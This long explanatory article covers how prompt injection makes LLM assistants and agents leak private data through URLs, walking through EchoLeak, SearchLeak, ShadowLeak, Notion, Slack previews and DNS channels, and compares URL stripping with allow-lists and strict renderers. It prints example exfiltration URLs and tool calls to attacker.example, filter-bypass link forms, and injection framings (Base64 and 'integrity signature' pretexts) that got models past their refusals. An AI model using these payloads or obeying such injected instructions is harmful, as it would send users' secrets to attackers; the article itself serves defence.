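# Data theft through links in language model outputs: why deleting URLs fails and how allow-lists and link rewriting work

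## How a link can carry private data out of a conversation

Data exfiltration through links is a way to steal private data from applications built on large language models, such as ChatGPT, Claude and Microsoft Copilot. An attacker gets the model to write the data into a web address on a server that the attacker controls, and the server receives the data when a person or a program requests that address. Researchers have demonstrated the method against most well-known chatbots since 2023. Vendors have closed many of the specific routes, usually within weeks, but researchers keep finding others.

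A small example shows each step. An assistant can read its user's mailbox. One message in it comes from the user's bank and contains the six-digit login code 482913. Another comes from an attacker, who does not know the code and cannot open the mailbox, but who can send mail to it as anyone can. The attack succeeds if some piece of software on the user's side requests this address:

```
https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913
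```

### What the server receives

*What is a URL?*, a page on MDN, Mozilla's reference site for web developers, explains what each part of a web address, or URL, does. Five of these parts matter here.

| Part | In the example | Does it reach the server? |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | It only sets the protocol for the request |
| Host | `attacker.example` | Yes; it selects the server |
| Path | `/logo.png` | Yes |
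| Query | `c=482913` | Yes |
| Fragment | none here; it would follow a `#` | No |

Whoever runs the server decides what the path and the query mean. No picture called logo.png has to exist. The server can answer with an error and the theft is complete all the same, because the request has already delivered the code. Websites commonly log the URLs that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, so the attacker needs no special software to collect the result. A line like this one in an ordinary log is enough:

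```
203.0.113.7  "GET /logo.png?c=482913"  404
```

HTTPS does not prevent this theft. It hides the path and query from others on the network, but the attacker's server receives the request and decrypts it.

An attacker can receive the code from almost any part of the address. `/482913.png` carries it in the path. `482913.attacker.example` carries it in the host name, which can reach the attacker's name server during the lookup, before any request for a page. Browsers never send the fragment to the server, but if the user opens the address as a page, a script on the page can read the fragment and send it on.

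### How the attacker gets the address written

The attacker uses indirect prompt injection, hiding instructions in content the model reads so that the model follows them as if its user had given them. This works because the model has no separate channel for commands. When the user asks for a summary of the day's mail, the application puts the request and the messages into one sequence of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes. Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that models cannot reliably rank instructions in that sequence by where they came from.

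In the example, the hostile email contains an instruction to end the summary with a picture and to put the most recent login code at the end of the picture's address. The attacker leaves a gap for the code, which the model can fill because the bank's message is in the same sequence as the email.

This attack requires three conditions, a combination Willison calls the "lethal trifecta". The system must have access to private data, take in content that an attacker can influence, and have some way to communicate with the outside. A mailbox alone meets the first two conditions, since it holds secrets and accepts text from strangers. The ability to display an image from any server meets the third.

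OpenAI's security staff use an older vocabulary for much the same analysis. An attacker needs a source, meaning a way to influence the system, and a sink, meaning a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, according to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026). The hostile email is the source and the image request is the sink. Private data has no term of its own in this scheme; it is what flows into the sink. (Some security writers use "source" for the point where the secret enters the system, so the word needs checking from one text to the next.)

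### Links, images and who sends the request

Chatbots usually write their answers in Markdown, a notation that marks formatting with punctuation. The renderer, the software that turns the model's text into the links and images on the screen, converts it into HTML, the language of web pages. A link and an image look almost the same in Markdown:

```
[Your invoice](https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913)
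![Company logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913)
```

Under the CommonMark specification, the two lines differ in syntax only by the exclamation mark at the start of the second. The first line becomes an `<a>` element, which displays the words "Your invoice" and does nothing until someone clicks them. The second becomes an `<img>` element. A browser has to fetch an image to display it, so by default it contacts the server as the answer appears. This is an automatic request, meaning that software sends it without a click. The image can be a single transparent pixel, which the user cannot see.

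The user and the browser are two of the four parties that may send the request. A user who clicks a link can check the address first, though the link's visible text may not resemble its destination. If the browser sends the request without a click, the user has no chance to check the address beforehand.

A messaging app may also send the private data. Many people now talk to assistants through Slack or Telegram, and these apps fetch a linked page to build a small preview of it. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that a preview makes the same type of network request as a click. An ordinary text link therefore becomes as dangerous as an image, since neither needs a click to send the data.

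An agent, a model that can use tools such as a web browser, can also fetch the address itself while it works, so the address never has to appear in an answer. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) showed on a local testbed that instructions hidden in the title and metadata of a malicious web page can make an agent send out sensitive context this way. If the agent runs on the vendor's computers, the request is a server-side fetch, which the user's browser neither detects nor controls.

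The right defense depends on which program makes the request. A rule inside the browser can stop the image in the example, but it has no effect on Telegram's preview or an agent's own fetch, even though all three requests would put the same line in the attacker's log.

### The disclosures of 2023

Security researcher Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the image leak to Microsoft and OpenAI in early April 2023. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* documents the Microsoft case. Text on a web page, such as a user comment or an advertisement, could take over Bing Chat when a visitor asked it about the page. A couple of turns later, the chatbot would write an image address containing an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from further down the page. Roman Samoilenko described the same weakness in ChatGPT that April, as Willison (2023) noted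 at the time. Microsoft's fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule set by a web page that limits which domains the browser may load images and other resources from. Embrace The Red's 2026 retrospective, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates that fix to May 2023, but Rehberger's original write-up gives 15 June, the day Microsoft notified him. Anthropic fixed the same flaw in Claude in July 2023, two weeks after Rehberger reported it. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* describes the fix, which required the user to click "Show Image" before the browser would load anything. OpenAI first declined to fix ChatGPT, then added a partial check in December 2023 and strengthened it around August 2025.

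Similar attacks followed across the industry. By June 2025, Willison had listed seventeen reported cases of data theft by prompt injection, including EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route through which the data left.

### Why defenders guard the way out

That choice is practical because a mail assistant without access to private data has nothing to do, and one that never reads text from strangers cannot read incoming mail. Limiting where requests may go leaves the assistant more useful, and Willison considers outbound requests by far the easiest of the three conditions to restrict. Ordinary code can also enforce such a limit. A program that checks a host name against a list gives the same result however persuasive the hostile email is, whereas a model refuses only with some probability. OpenAI's Lockdown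 Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that became available in June 2026, follows this reasoning by limiting outbound requests rather than trying to keep injections out of the content ChatGPT reads.

Models have become much better at resisting prompt injections, but some still succeed, so there is still reason to block the routes by which data can leave a conversation. According to OpenAI, most attempts to make ChatGPT pass on secrets fail because the model refuses. The attacks that still work resemble the tricks fraudsters play on people. One email from 2025 posed as a colleague's follow-up on restructuring documents and succeeded in half of the test runs.

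The strongest recent evidence of resistance to indirect injection comes from Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, in its "auto mode", where an automated classifier reviews each action in place of the user. Anthropic commissioned the firm Trajectory Labs to attack it with 72 injection scenarios, ten times each. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that none of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three current Claude models. Even with auto mode's checks switched off, the average success rate was 0.09%, so most of the resistance comes from the models themselves. Other vendors' models may be less resistant, as 5.83% of attempts succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol running in OpenAI's Codex with a comparable review mode.

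Zero out of 720 is impressive, but it is a weaker guarantee than it sounds because the runs cover only 72 scenarios, each repeated ten times. Trajectory Labs had also tuned the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, while a real attacker can study the current one and keep trying. Willison (2026) asked for more independent confirmation, and within three weeks of Anthropic's announcement Rehberger published an attack that got past auto mode. As Crosley notes in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, Rehberger's samples were small, with three or four successes in five runs depending on the configuration. They still show that the true success rate for a determined attacker is not zero.

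An experiment on an older model shows most clearly how much wording can affect whether an attack succeeds. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) gave GPT-4o a dummy secret token, a policy against sending it anywhere except one trusted host, and the task of summarising a web page that contained an injection. The model could either finish or post data to an address, using a mock tool that only recorded what it received. Ten openly worded types of attack all failed. Rahman and Kim then requested the same leak under other descriptions, such as an "integrity signature" that the model had to append to its summary. Two of these framings worked in every trial. Across all eight variants, the success rate was 40.0% in one run and 31.9% in another, which gives an idea of how much results vary between runs.

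They next tried to repair the policy. A version that listed the forbidden behaviours and barred transmitting the token "in any form" cut the leak rate from 31.9% to 0%. When they dropped that phrase, the rate rose to 48.8%. It had been 38.1% with no confidentiality policy at all, so the narrower wording apparently didn't help. A developer who wrote it would have little reason to suspect this, because it reads like a careful instruction.

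These percentages are not leak rates for a current product, because GPT-4o dates from 2024, the agent took a single step, and Rahman and Kim reached the model through OpenAI's programming interface. When they tried several of the pages on ChatGPT, the attack failed in all 48 valid trials. So the experiment does not contradict the Claude Code result, which concerns newer models with a classifier around them. But it does give a reason to distrust any defence that depends on how a request is phrased, because Rahman and Kim estimate that an attacker who tried three wordings of the "signature" trick would have succeeded about 96% of the time.

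Searching the outgoing data for the secret has a similar weakness. Rahman and Kim built a filter that recognised the token in plain text, reversed and in several common encodings. It missed every leak where the model had used ROT13, a simple letter substitution they had not anticipated. In the mailbox example, a filter that looks for 482913 in outgoing addresses will miss the reversed code, 319284, and one that also checks for reversed digits will miss the code with 1 added to each digit.

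Checking the destination avoids both problems because it doesn't require interpreting the email or recognising the code. When Rahman and Kim allowed the agent to post only to the trusted host, the leak rate was necessarily 0%, whatever the wording or the encoding. However, the agent could no longer send anything to any other host, even when the user wanted it to.

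## Why filters that delete URLs miss some of them

The simplest way to control where data can go is to allow no destinations at all, by deleting every web address from the model's answer before the user sees it. This is URL stripping. A basic version takes four steps:

1. The application receives the model's answer as Markdown text.
2. A filter searches the text for a pattern that describes links and images.
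3. The filter deletes every match, or puts a marker such as "[link removed]" in its place.
4. The renderer converts the remaining text into HTML, and the browser displays it.

The pattern is usually a regular expression, a compact notation for describing text. This one covers both the link and the image from the mailbox example:

```
!?\[[^\]]*\]\(https?://[^)]*\)
```

The filter matches, from left to right, an optional exclamation mark, some text in square brackets, an opening round bracket, `http://` or `https://`, and everything up to the closing round bracket. If the assistant ends its summary with the "Company logo" image, the filter deletes the whole line, including the code 482913, and the browser never contacts attacker.example. A developer who tests the filter on that example will conclude that it works.

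A filter that deletes URLs works if its pattern covers every form of link and image the renderer accepts, and if it runs before the browser acts on the text. Two attacks got past Microsoft's filter for Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches a user's work email, files and chats. EchoLeak, published in June 2025, used a form of link that the filter did not cover. SearchLeak, published a year later, sent its request before the filter ran.

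### Links that the pattern does not cover

Markdown lets a writer put an address elsewhere in the text and refer to it by a label. This is a reference-style image:

```
![Company logo][ref]

[ref]: https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913
```

The renderer joins the two pieces and produces the same `<img>` element as before. The pattern above requires a round bracket straight after the square ones. There is none here, so the filter leaves both lines unchanged. Markdown also has shorter variants, in which the description also serves as the label.

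Copilot's filter had this gap. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explains how Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, found the gap and built an attack around it. The attacker only had to send an employee an email. Copilot retrieves messages that seem relevant to the user's question, so the email had no effect until the employee asked about something it seemed to cover. To make retrieval more likely, Aim Labs wrote one long email with sections on many common office topics, such as onboarding and leave, and repeated the injected instructions in each. Microsoft's classifier for catching such instructions missed them because the email addressed the human recipient and never mentioned an AI.

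Once Copilot had retrieved the email, it followed its instructions and put the most sensitive information it could find into a URL. Copilot redacted external links and images written in the ordinary Markdown form, but not those written in reference style. Aim Labs first used a link and then switched to an image, which loads without a click.

At that point Microsoft's CSP stopped the attack for a while. Copilot's page permitted images from just under thirty sources, mostly Microsoft services, and the browser refused to load anything from the attacker's server. Aim Labs therefore looked for a permitted service that would fetch an outside address on request, as large services often do to build previews. SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, had one, but it worked only if the victim had first accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A preview service in Microsoft Teams had no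 such condition. The finished image address had roughly this shape:

```
https://permitted.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/482913
```

The browser contacts permitted.example, which the CSP allows. That service then requests the second address from its own servers, where the page's CSP does not apply, and the code arrives in the attacker's log.

Microsoft has patched EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). The case study *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), which draws on published material, dates the vulnerability's discovery to January 2025 and the fix to May, a month before the public disclosure. Microsoft made the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. It reported no sign that anyone had used the attack.

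A developer could extend the pattern to cover reference-style links. That would close this gap, but other forms remain, depending on the renderer:

| Text in the model's answer | How it can become a link or image |
|---|---|
| `<img src="https://attacker.example/482913.png">` | Some Markdown renderers pass raw HTML through |
| `www.attacker.example/482913` | Some renderers turn bare "www." text into a link |
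| `![Logo](//attacker.example/482913.png)` | The browser fills in the missing `https:` from the page's own address |
| `![Logo](https&#58;//attacker.example/482913.png)` | The renderer decodes `&#58;` into a colon |

A much broader pattern that deletes anything starting with `https://` would catch the HTML tag and the reference-style definition but miss the other three rows. The "www." form comes from GitHub's dialect of Markdown, and examples in PyMarkdown's documentation show that it produces a working link without brackets or a scheme. A filter that used to catch every link can therefore start missing some when someone updates the renderer or turns on an extension.

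These are all cases of parser mismatch, where the program that checks the text interprets it differently from the program that displays it. Websites had this problem before chatbots existed. They often run untrusted HTML through a sanitiser, a program that removes dangerous elements, and then pass the cleaned string to the browser, which parses it again. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* warns that vulnerabilities can arise when the second parse gives a different result from the first. The risk is greater when a filter checks Markdown with a regular expression, which interprets the text much more crudely than a real parser does.

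After EchoLeak, Microsoft (2025) listed "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods" among its defences against indirect prompt injection. Such blocking is limited to known methods, because a filter that lists forbidden forms protects against a new one only after somebody has found it.

### Requests that leave before the filter runs

Chatbots normally stream their answers, displaying the text while the model is still writing it. A filter that runs on the finished answer is too late, because the browser has already acted on the unfinished text.

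Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot Enterprise Search that exploited this delay. The victim had to click a link, but it led to a genuine Microsoft address. The search page read the user's query from the address's `q` parameter, and Copilot followed it as a prompt, so an attacker could put instructions in the link itself, without a hostile email in the mailbox. In the demonstration, the instructions made Copilot look up an email and write its title into the address of an image. Email titles are worth stealing because services often put login codes in them.

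Microsoft's protection was to wrap Copilot's output in a code block, so that the browser would show any HTML tags as harmless text. In one respect this is better than deleting links, because it does not depend on recognising each way of writing an address. But the page applied it at the end:

1. Copilot starts to stream an answer that contains an `<img>` tag.
2. The browser creates the image element and requests the image.
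3. Copilot finishes the answer.
4. The page wraps the answer in a code block, and the image turns into text.

The browser sent out the email title in step 2. Programmers call this kind of error a race condition because the result depends on which of two processes finishes first. Here the browser finished first whenever the tag arrived before the end of the answer.

As in EchoLeak, the CSP prevented the browser from contacting the attacker directly, but a permitted service relayed the request. The CSP allowed images from bing.com, and Bing's search-by-image feature accepts the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch. The attacker could therefore give Bing an address on the attacker's server that contained the email title. Bing was already on the list of permitted sources that Ravia had published with EchoLeak the year before.

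SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) no longer works. Microsoft's 4 June advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), describes the flaw as fully mitigated, with no known exploitation and no action required from customers. Varonis published its account of SearchLeak eleven days later.

The published severity ratings conflict. Microsoft labelled the flaw "Critical" but scored it 6.5 out of 10 on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System, which counts as medium. *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026), an article in The Hacker News, gives a score of 7.5, or high, from the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), but The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* puts both scores at 6.5. The change history on a vulnerability-tracking site, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability*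 (2026), supports the higher NVD figure. It shows that NVD analysts added their own assessment on 8 June, which differs from Microsoft's only in recording that the attack needs no action by the user. Microsoft's entry looks correct, since the victim has to click a link.

For EchoLeak, Microsoft gave the higher score instead. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) cites 9.3 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the NVD. Microsoft therefore rated EchoLeak much more severe than the other vulnerability, while the NVD rated the two equally.

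Streaming had already caused a leak in another product. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, published in May 2025, describes an attack on Duo, the assistant built into GitLab, a site where programmers store and review code. Duo converted its answers to HTML line by line, before it could determine whether a line belonged to a code block. An `<img>` tag that arrived early enough became a live image, and in the demonstration the image's address contained private source code.

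Duo ran its output through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser designed mainly to stop injected scripts. By default, DOMPurify leaves images, forms and links in place, so with those settings it would have let the image through even if the check had run at the right time. GitLab has since patched Duo so that it does not render such tags if they point to domains outside gitlab.com.

Running the filter on each fragment as it arrives does not solve the timing problem either, because a URL can be split between two fragments. The application may receive `![Logo](htt` and then `ps://attacker.example/482913.png)`, neither of which matches the filter's pattern. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) therefore recommends rechecking all the text received so far whenever more arrives, and abandoning the answer as soon as the sanitiser removes anything.

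This is sound advice against injected scripts, the threat the guide addresses, but it does much less against data theft through images. The guide's sample code runs the HTML sanitiser before the Markdown parser, when a Markdown image is still plain text, with no HTML for the sanitiser to remove. A developer who copied the sample unchanged would still need a separate rule for images.

### Filters that delete only part of an address

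Some filters keep the link and delete only the part that looks most likely to carry data. The usual candidate is the query, the part after the question mark. This is what happens to three versions of the same theft:

| Address the model writes | After the filter deletes the query | Does the code still leak? |
|---|---|---|
| `https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913` | `https://attacker.example/logo.png` | No |
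| `https://attacker.example/482913.png` | unchanged | Yes, in the path |
| `https://482913.attacker.example/logo.png` | unchanged | Yes, in the host name |

The attacker can put the secret in a part of the URL that the filter keeps. In Reddy and Gujral's illustration of EchoLeak's image URL, the secret is in the path.

Deleting queries is more useful on domains that the application already trusts, which is where Reddy and Gujral suggest it. Both Copilot attacks put the attacker's entire URL inside the query of a Microsoft service's URL. Without that query, Teams and Bing would have had nothing to fetch. Deleting queries would not stop a relay that takes the outside URL in its path, and it breaks legitimate links that need their queries, such as links to search results.

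A stricter filter could also delete the path and keep only the host name, but this would miss the link in the third row of the table, which carries the code in the host name itself. Shortening the host name to the registered domain, here attacker.example, removes the code, though an attacker who owns several domains can still convey a little information by which one appears. The link then leads only to a site's front page, so a legitimate link to a particular article or invoice also loses most of its usefulness.

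Even a filter that completely deletes every URL it finds can miss an address written out in words. The assistant might tell its user to confirm the login by visiting "attacker dot example, slash 482913", which a pattern that searches for web addresses would not match. The user would have to type the address by hand, so the attack is slower and more conspicuous than one that uses an invisible image, and many people would presumably refuse. A filter that tried to catch such sentences would have to recognise every way of describing an address, which is much the same problem as in Rahman and Kim's search for encoded secrets.

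### A renderer that refuses links by default

In a better design, the renderer has a short list of things that an answer may contain and refuses everything else, rather than searching for addresses.

It begins by parsing the text with the same parser that will produce the page. The parser's output is a tree, in which each node is a paragraph, a list, a link and so on. All the forms of image in the earlier examples end up either as an image node or, if the model wrote raw HTML, as an HTML node. The renderer no longer needs to know how the model spelled the address. It goes through the tree and applies a rule for each kind of node:

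```
plain text                              -> the same text
paragraph, heading, list, table,
emphasis, code                          -> the matching HTML element
link                                    -> its visible text, no address
image                                   -> its description, as plain text
anything else                           -> "[removed]"
```

The last line is the most important because it covers nodes added later, such as those from an extension for diagrams or formulas. These fall under "anything else" until a developer has considered whether they can trigger requests. A list of forbidden forms would let them through by default.

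The visible text of a link can also be an address, so the renderer should show a marker in that case. It should not copy attributes from the model's text into the elements it creates, because a style attribute can also make a browser load an image. It should also build the page's elements directly from the tree, because writing out a string of HTML for the browser to parse again brings back the risk of a mismatch.

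This design also removes the race condition that SearchLeak exploited. The renderer has no code that creates links or images, so a partly streamed answer is as safe as a finished one. It still makes sense to hold back an unfinished link during streaming, because otherwise the raw address appears briefly before the closing bracket arrives.

A renderer that permits some links must hold back each link until it is complete. Suppose the renderer allows trusted.example and the text so far ends with `https://trusted.example`. The next fragment may be `.attacker.example/482913`, which makes the full link point to the attacker's domain. A renderer that approved the link after the first fragment would have checked the wrong host.

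Streamdown, a component for displaying streamed Markdown, covers part of this. It shows a placeholder for a link or image until its Markdown is complete, as Streamdown's *Unterminated Block Parsing* explains. That prevents the trusted.example mistake, but it does not make an image safe, because Streamdown loads the real picture once the image's closing bracket arrives, even if the rest of the answer is still on its way. According to Streamdown's *Security*, the default settings allow images and links from anywhere, and developers should tighten them for untrusted content. The same page shows how to restrict images to chosen addresses and ignore raw HTML.

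TanStack Markdown, a similar component, has one stricter default, which is to display raw HTML as text. TanStack's *Security* also describes a hook that lets developers inspect each link and image address during parsing. This includes reference-style addresses, so the syntax that got past Copilot's filter would not get past the hook. But TanStack Markdown allows ordinary web links by default, and the developer has to write the rule that blocks them.

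A CSP can back up the renderer in case a programming error lets an image element through. If the page never needs to show images, its policy can block them all with `img-src 'none'`. EchoLeak and SearchLeak both depended on a permitted service that would relay a request, and this setting permits no image sources. It doesn't affect links that a user clicks, so the renderer still has to remove those.

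Together, these measures stop automatic requests from model-written images in that one chat window. The browser has no image to load, no matter what the attacker got the model to write or how. The measures also remove every model-written link the user could click, including legitimate ones.

Google accepted weaker protection against data theft so that Gemini could keep showing links. Gemini's sanitiser blocks external images, which prevents leaks like EchoLeak, but Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* shows that an ordinary link can still carry data out when the user clicks it. Google removes links that its Safe Browsing service recognises as malicious, but an attacker can avoid that list by registering a new domain. Google closed Checkmarx's report in October 2025, saying a fix was infeasible. Checkmarx also got Microsoft's Copilot Chat to leak an access key through an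 image, without a click. Microsoft closed that report the next month without a fix, arguing that the attack needed several non-default user actions and was unreliable.

Even the strictest renderer controls only what its own window displays. An address left as plain text can become a live link again if the user pastes the answer into a messaging app, which parses text by its own rules. The company's mobile app may use a different renderer with different gaps, and an agent's own requests bypass the renderer altogether.

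## What injected instructions can still do outside the chat window

If a company adopts the strict renderer, its chat window shows no links and loads no images, but the hostile email still reaches the model. The model can then deliver the login code to the attacker by calling a tool or by writing text for another program, and a filter on the chat window's answers doesn't check either one.

### Requests from the agent's own tools

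In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the victim's browser made the first request, so the page's CSP at least limited where that request could go. An agent with a browsing tool can send requests without the victim's browser. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that reads sources for up to half an hour and then writes a report. Users can connect it to Gmail so that it reads their mail as well as the web.

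Radware's demonstration stole an employee's name and address from a message in the victim's inbox. With the login code from the earlier example in their place, the attack runs like this:

1. The user asks Deep Research to go through the day's email.
2. The agent reads the bank's message and the attacker's, which contains hidden instructions.
3. The model calls its browsing tool with the address `https://attacker.example/482913`.
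4. OpenAI's servers request that address.
5. The model writes its report.

By the time an output filter checks the report in step 5, the code is already in the attacker's log. The employer's web gateway cannot stop the request either, because it travels from OpenAI's servers to the attacker's without crossing the employer's network.

The model refused plain requests to send personal data to an outside address, and sometimes searched for a suspicious address instead of opening it. Radware got further by naming the browsing tool and telling the model to retry after failures, but the model still left the personal data out of the address. Radware then told it to encode the data in Base64, a standard way of rewriting data as letters and digits, on the pretext that this would protect the data. Radware reports that this version worked every time in repeated tests. It closely resembles the restructuring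 email that, according to OpenAI, worked in half of the test runs, so the success rate probably depended on the variant.

OpenAI already restricted which image addresses ChatGPT would display, but Radware saw no similar restriction on which addresses the browsing tool could open. OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak in early August 2025, about seven weeks after Radware reported it. A later attack, ZombieAgent, leaked data by choosing among prewritten addresses instead of composing one.

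The same weakness appeared a year later in Rovo, an agent that works across Atlassian's products for tracking tasks and sharing documents. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes how a hidden instruction in an uploaded file made Rovo add the contents of internal tickets and documents to an attacker's URL and then open it. The attack worked even when the organisation had switched off web search, because that setting left Rovo with the tool for opening search results. A user who reopened the chat later would find the ticket suggestions they had asked for but no trace of the request to the attacker's URL. PromptArmor reported the flaw to Atlassian in May 2026 and published more than two months later, when Rovo was still vulnerable.

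A tool can also make web requests without looking like a browser. Notion, a workspace app for notes and databases, released version 3.0 in September 2025 with agents that could search the web. Willison, in *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*, describes an attack that Abi Raghuram published the next day. Hidden white text in a PDF told the agent to read a list of clients, join the entries into one string and add it to a web address. The agent then passed the address to the search tool. In the mailbox example, the call would look roughly like this:

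```
search("https://attacker.example/482913")
```

The search tool accepted an address as well as search terms, so the call sent the data to the attacker's server. A developer who reviewed the agent's permissions would have seen only a harmless-sounding search function.

Willison suggested that Notion stop the tool from accepting addresses. According to The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025), Notion responded by improving its detection of injections and requiring the user's approval before an agent opens a suspicious or model-generated link. Administrators can also turn off web access. The approval step should cover the demonstrated leak if Notion applies it to addresses in search queries, but the protection then depends on the user's judgement. In an Anthropic study that Willison discusses, a coding agent asked 1,053 paid testers for permission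 to run a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% refused. A web request with a plausible explanation is arguably harder to judge than such a command.

Code that an assistant runs can also send data. ChatGPT analyses files by running code in an isolated environment that is supposed to have no direct internet access. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes how data could leave through DNS, the system that translates host names into network addresses. To send the data, the code only had to look up a host name containing it, such as `482913.attacker.example`. OpenAI fixed this on 20 February 2026, and The Hacker News (2026) reports no evidence that anyone had used it maliciously.

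### Previews in messaging apps

A chatbot that answers through Slack or Telegram has no chat window of its own, so its developer has to deal with the messaging app's link previews.

PromptArmor tested such previews with OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant that people often use through Telegram. PromptArmor set up a site that records preview requests so that users could check whether their assistant leaked data. OpenClaw leaked data with its default Telegram settings. The leak stopped when PromptArmor set `linkPreview` to `false` in OpenClaw's configuration file. In August 2026, OpenClaw's Telegram documentation still listed previews as on by default, so each user has to know about the risk and change the setting.

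According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, its servers must also fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. Slack decides whether to show a preview only after this fetch, so a message may have leaked data even if no preview appears.

The program that posts the message can prevent the fetch by setting two options:

```
"unfurl_links": false,
"unfurl_media": false
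```

Slack stops fetching a link in a message only when the developer sets both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false. The first covers pages of text, and the second covers images, video and audio. Slack's documentation now advises developers to consider doing this for messages written by a language model. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* also describes a personal setting for people who would "prefer not to see previews". That setting is not a reliable protection, because hiding a preview is different from preventing the request.

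A developer could instead delete links from the message before posting it, but the filter would have to recognize Slack's link syntax. Slack writes a link as `<https://attacker.example/482913|Your invoice>`, which the regular expression in the previous section does not match.

Link previews also defeat the precaution of letting an agent post only where outsiders cannot read. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes Rehberger's test of Anthropic's Slack connector for agents, which he set up to post to a single private channel. A user might reasonably let the agent post there without asking each time. But when an injected instruction made the agent post a link containing a secret, Slack's servers fetched the link to preview it and sent the secret to the attacker, who didn't need access to the channel. If the link pointed to an image, several of Slack's bots requested it, so the secret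 leaked more than once.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Two days later, Anthropic archived the connector and announced that it would not fix security flaws in its archived connectors, so this one remains unpatched. It still had more than 14,000 downloads a week when Rehberger published the advisory. Anyone still running it has to add the two options by hand.

### Text that another program displays later

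The model's text can also sit in storage and leak data only when a different program displays it. This happened with Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that works with a user's files, email and calendar. It normally asks for permission before sending an email or posting in Teams, but PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that it did not ask when the recipient was the user, and that users had no setting to change this. The message could contain an image from an outside server, and Teams or Outlook requested that image when the user opened the message, so data could reach the server even though the user was the only recipient.

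PromptArmor hid the instructions in a skill, a file of reusable directions for the agent. They took up five of its 81 lines. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Copilot Cowork did the following:

1. It looked up recently edited documents and obtained download links for them that work without a login.
2. It put those links into the addresses of images on the attacker's server.
3. It sent the user a Teams message containing the images.

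Opening the message sent the download links to the attacker, who could then fetch the files. A short URL could therefore leak a document of any length. Copilot Cowork's window listed the Teams message among its completed actions but did not show the malicious content, even when the user clicked the entry.

The attack worked in all five trials. PromptArmor also ran it on Claude Opus 4.7, the more advanced of the two models that Copilot Cowork chose between automatically. Opus 4.7 leaked more because it searched more thoroughly for recent documents and found more to send.

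PromptArmor published this in May 2026 as a risk in the product's design and reported no fix. It suggested that administrators block downloads of sensitive files, which would keep Copilot Cowork from obtaining download links for them. The drawback is considerable, because users can then view those files only in a browser, not in apps such as Word and Excel.

An answer that a filter blocks can leak in the same way if the system keeps a copy. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows this with a mock banking application that checks customers' identities. The application gave a model six sources about a customer, including a scraped web page that contained an injection. The model produced an image address containing the customer's personal data. A second model, which checked answers before display, flagged this one, and the application withheld it from the user.

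The defence had worked, but OpenAI's developer platform had logged the answer. When a developer opened the log to find out what had gone wrong, the log viewer rendered the Markdown, and the developer's browser requested the image from the attacker's server. The application's own CSP could not have blocked this request because the log viewer is a separate page on OpenAI's site.

Filtering can make such a review more likely. PromptArmor gives the example of an answer in Perplexity, an AI search engine, that was blank because the software had removed a malicious image. A puzzled user may well click "thumbs down", which brings the original answer to a developer's attention.

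The service that triages reports for OpenAI closed this report in December 2025 as not applicable. OpenAI reopened it on 22 January 2026, after PromptArmor published its findings, and confirmed the flaw. As of July 2026, PromptArmor's page still described the fix as under way. Developers whose log viewer doesn't display answers as plain text can avoid the problem by reading suspicious answers in a tool that does.

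### An experiment with requests that leave no trace

These cases show that the routes exist, but a few demonstrations cannot show how often a check on the answer would miss a leak. Lan and colleagues tried to measure this by recording what reached a simulated attacker's server. They ran qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about seven billion parameters, on their own hardware. The user always asked the model to summarise a web page, and the page contained an instruction to send a secret from the model's context to the attacker's server.

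They put the instruction in the page's title, its description metadata, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through a chain of redirects. The instruction was for the model to send the secret either whole or in four pieces, each in a separate request. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The model sent a request to the attacker in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88%. (The paper's headline figure of about 89% is the rate for the runs with redirects.) The model sent none in 120 control runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the final answer looked normal, so a check of it would have found nothing wrong.

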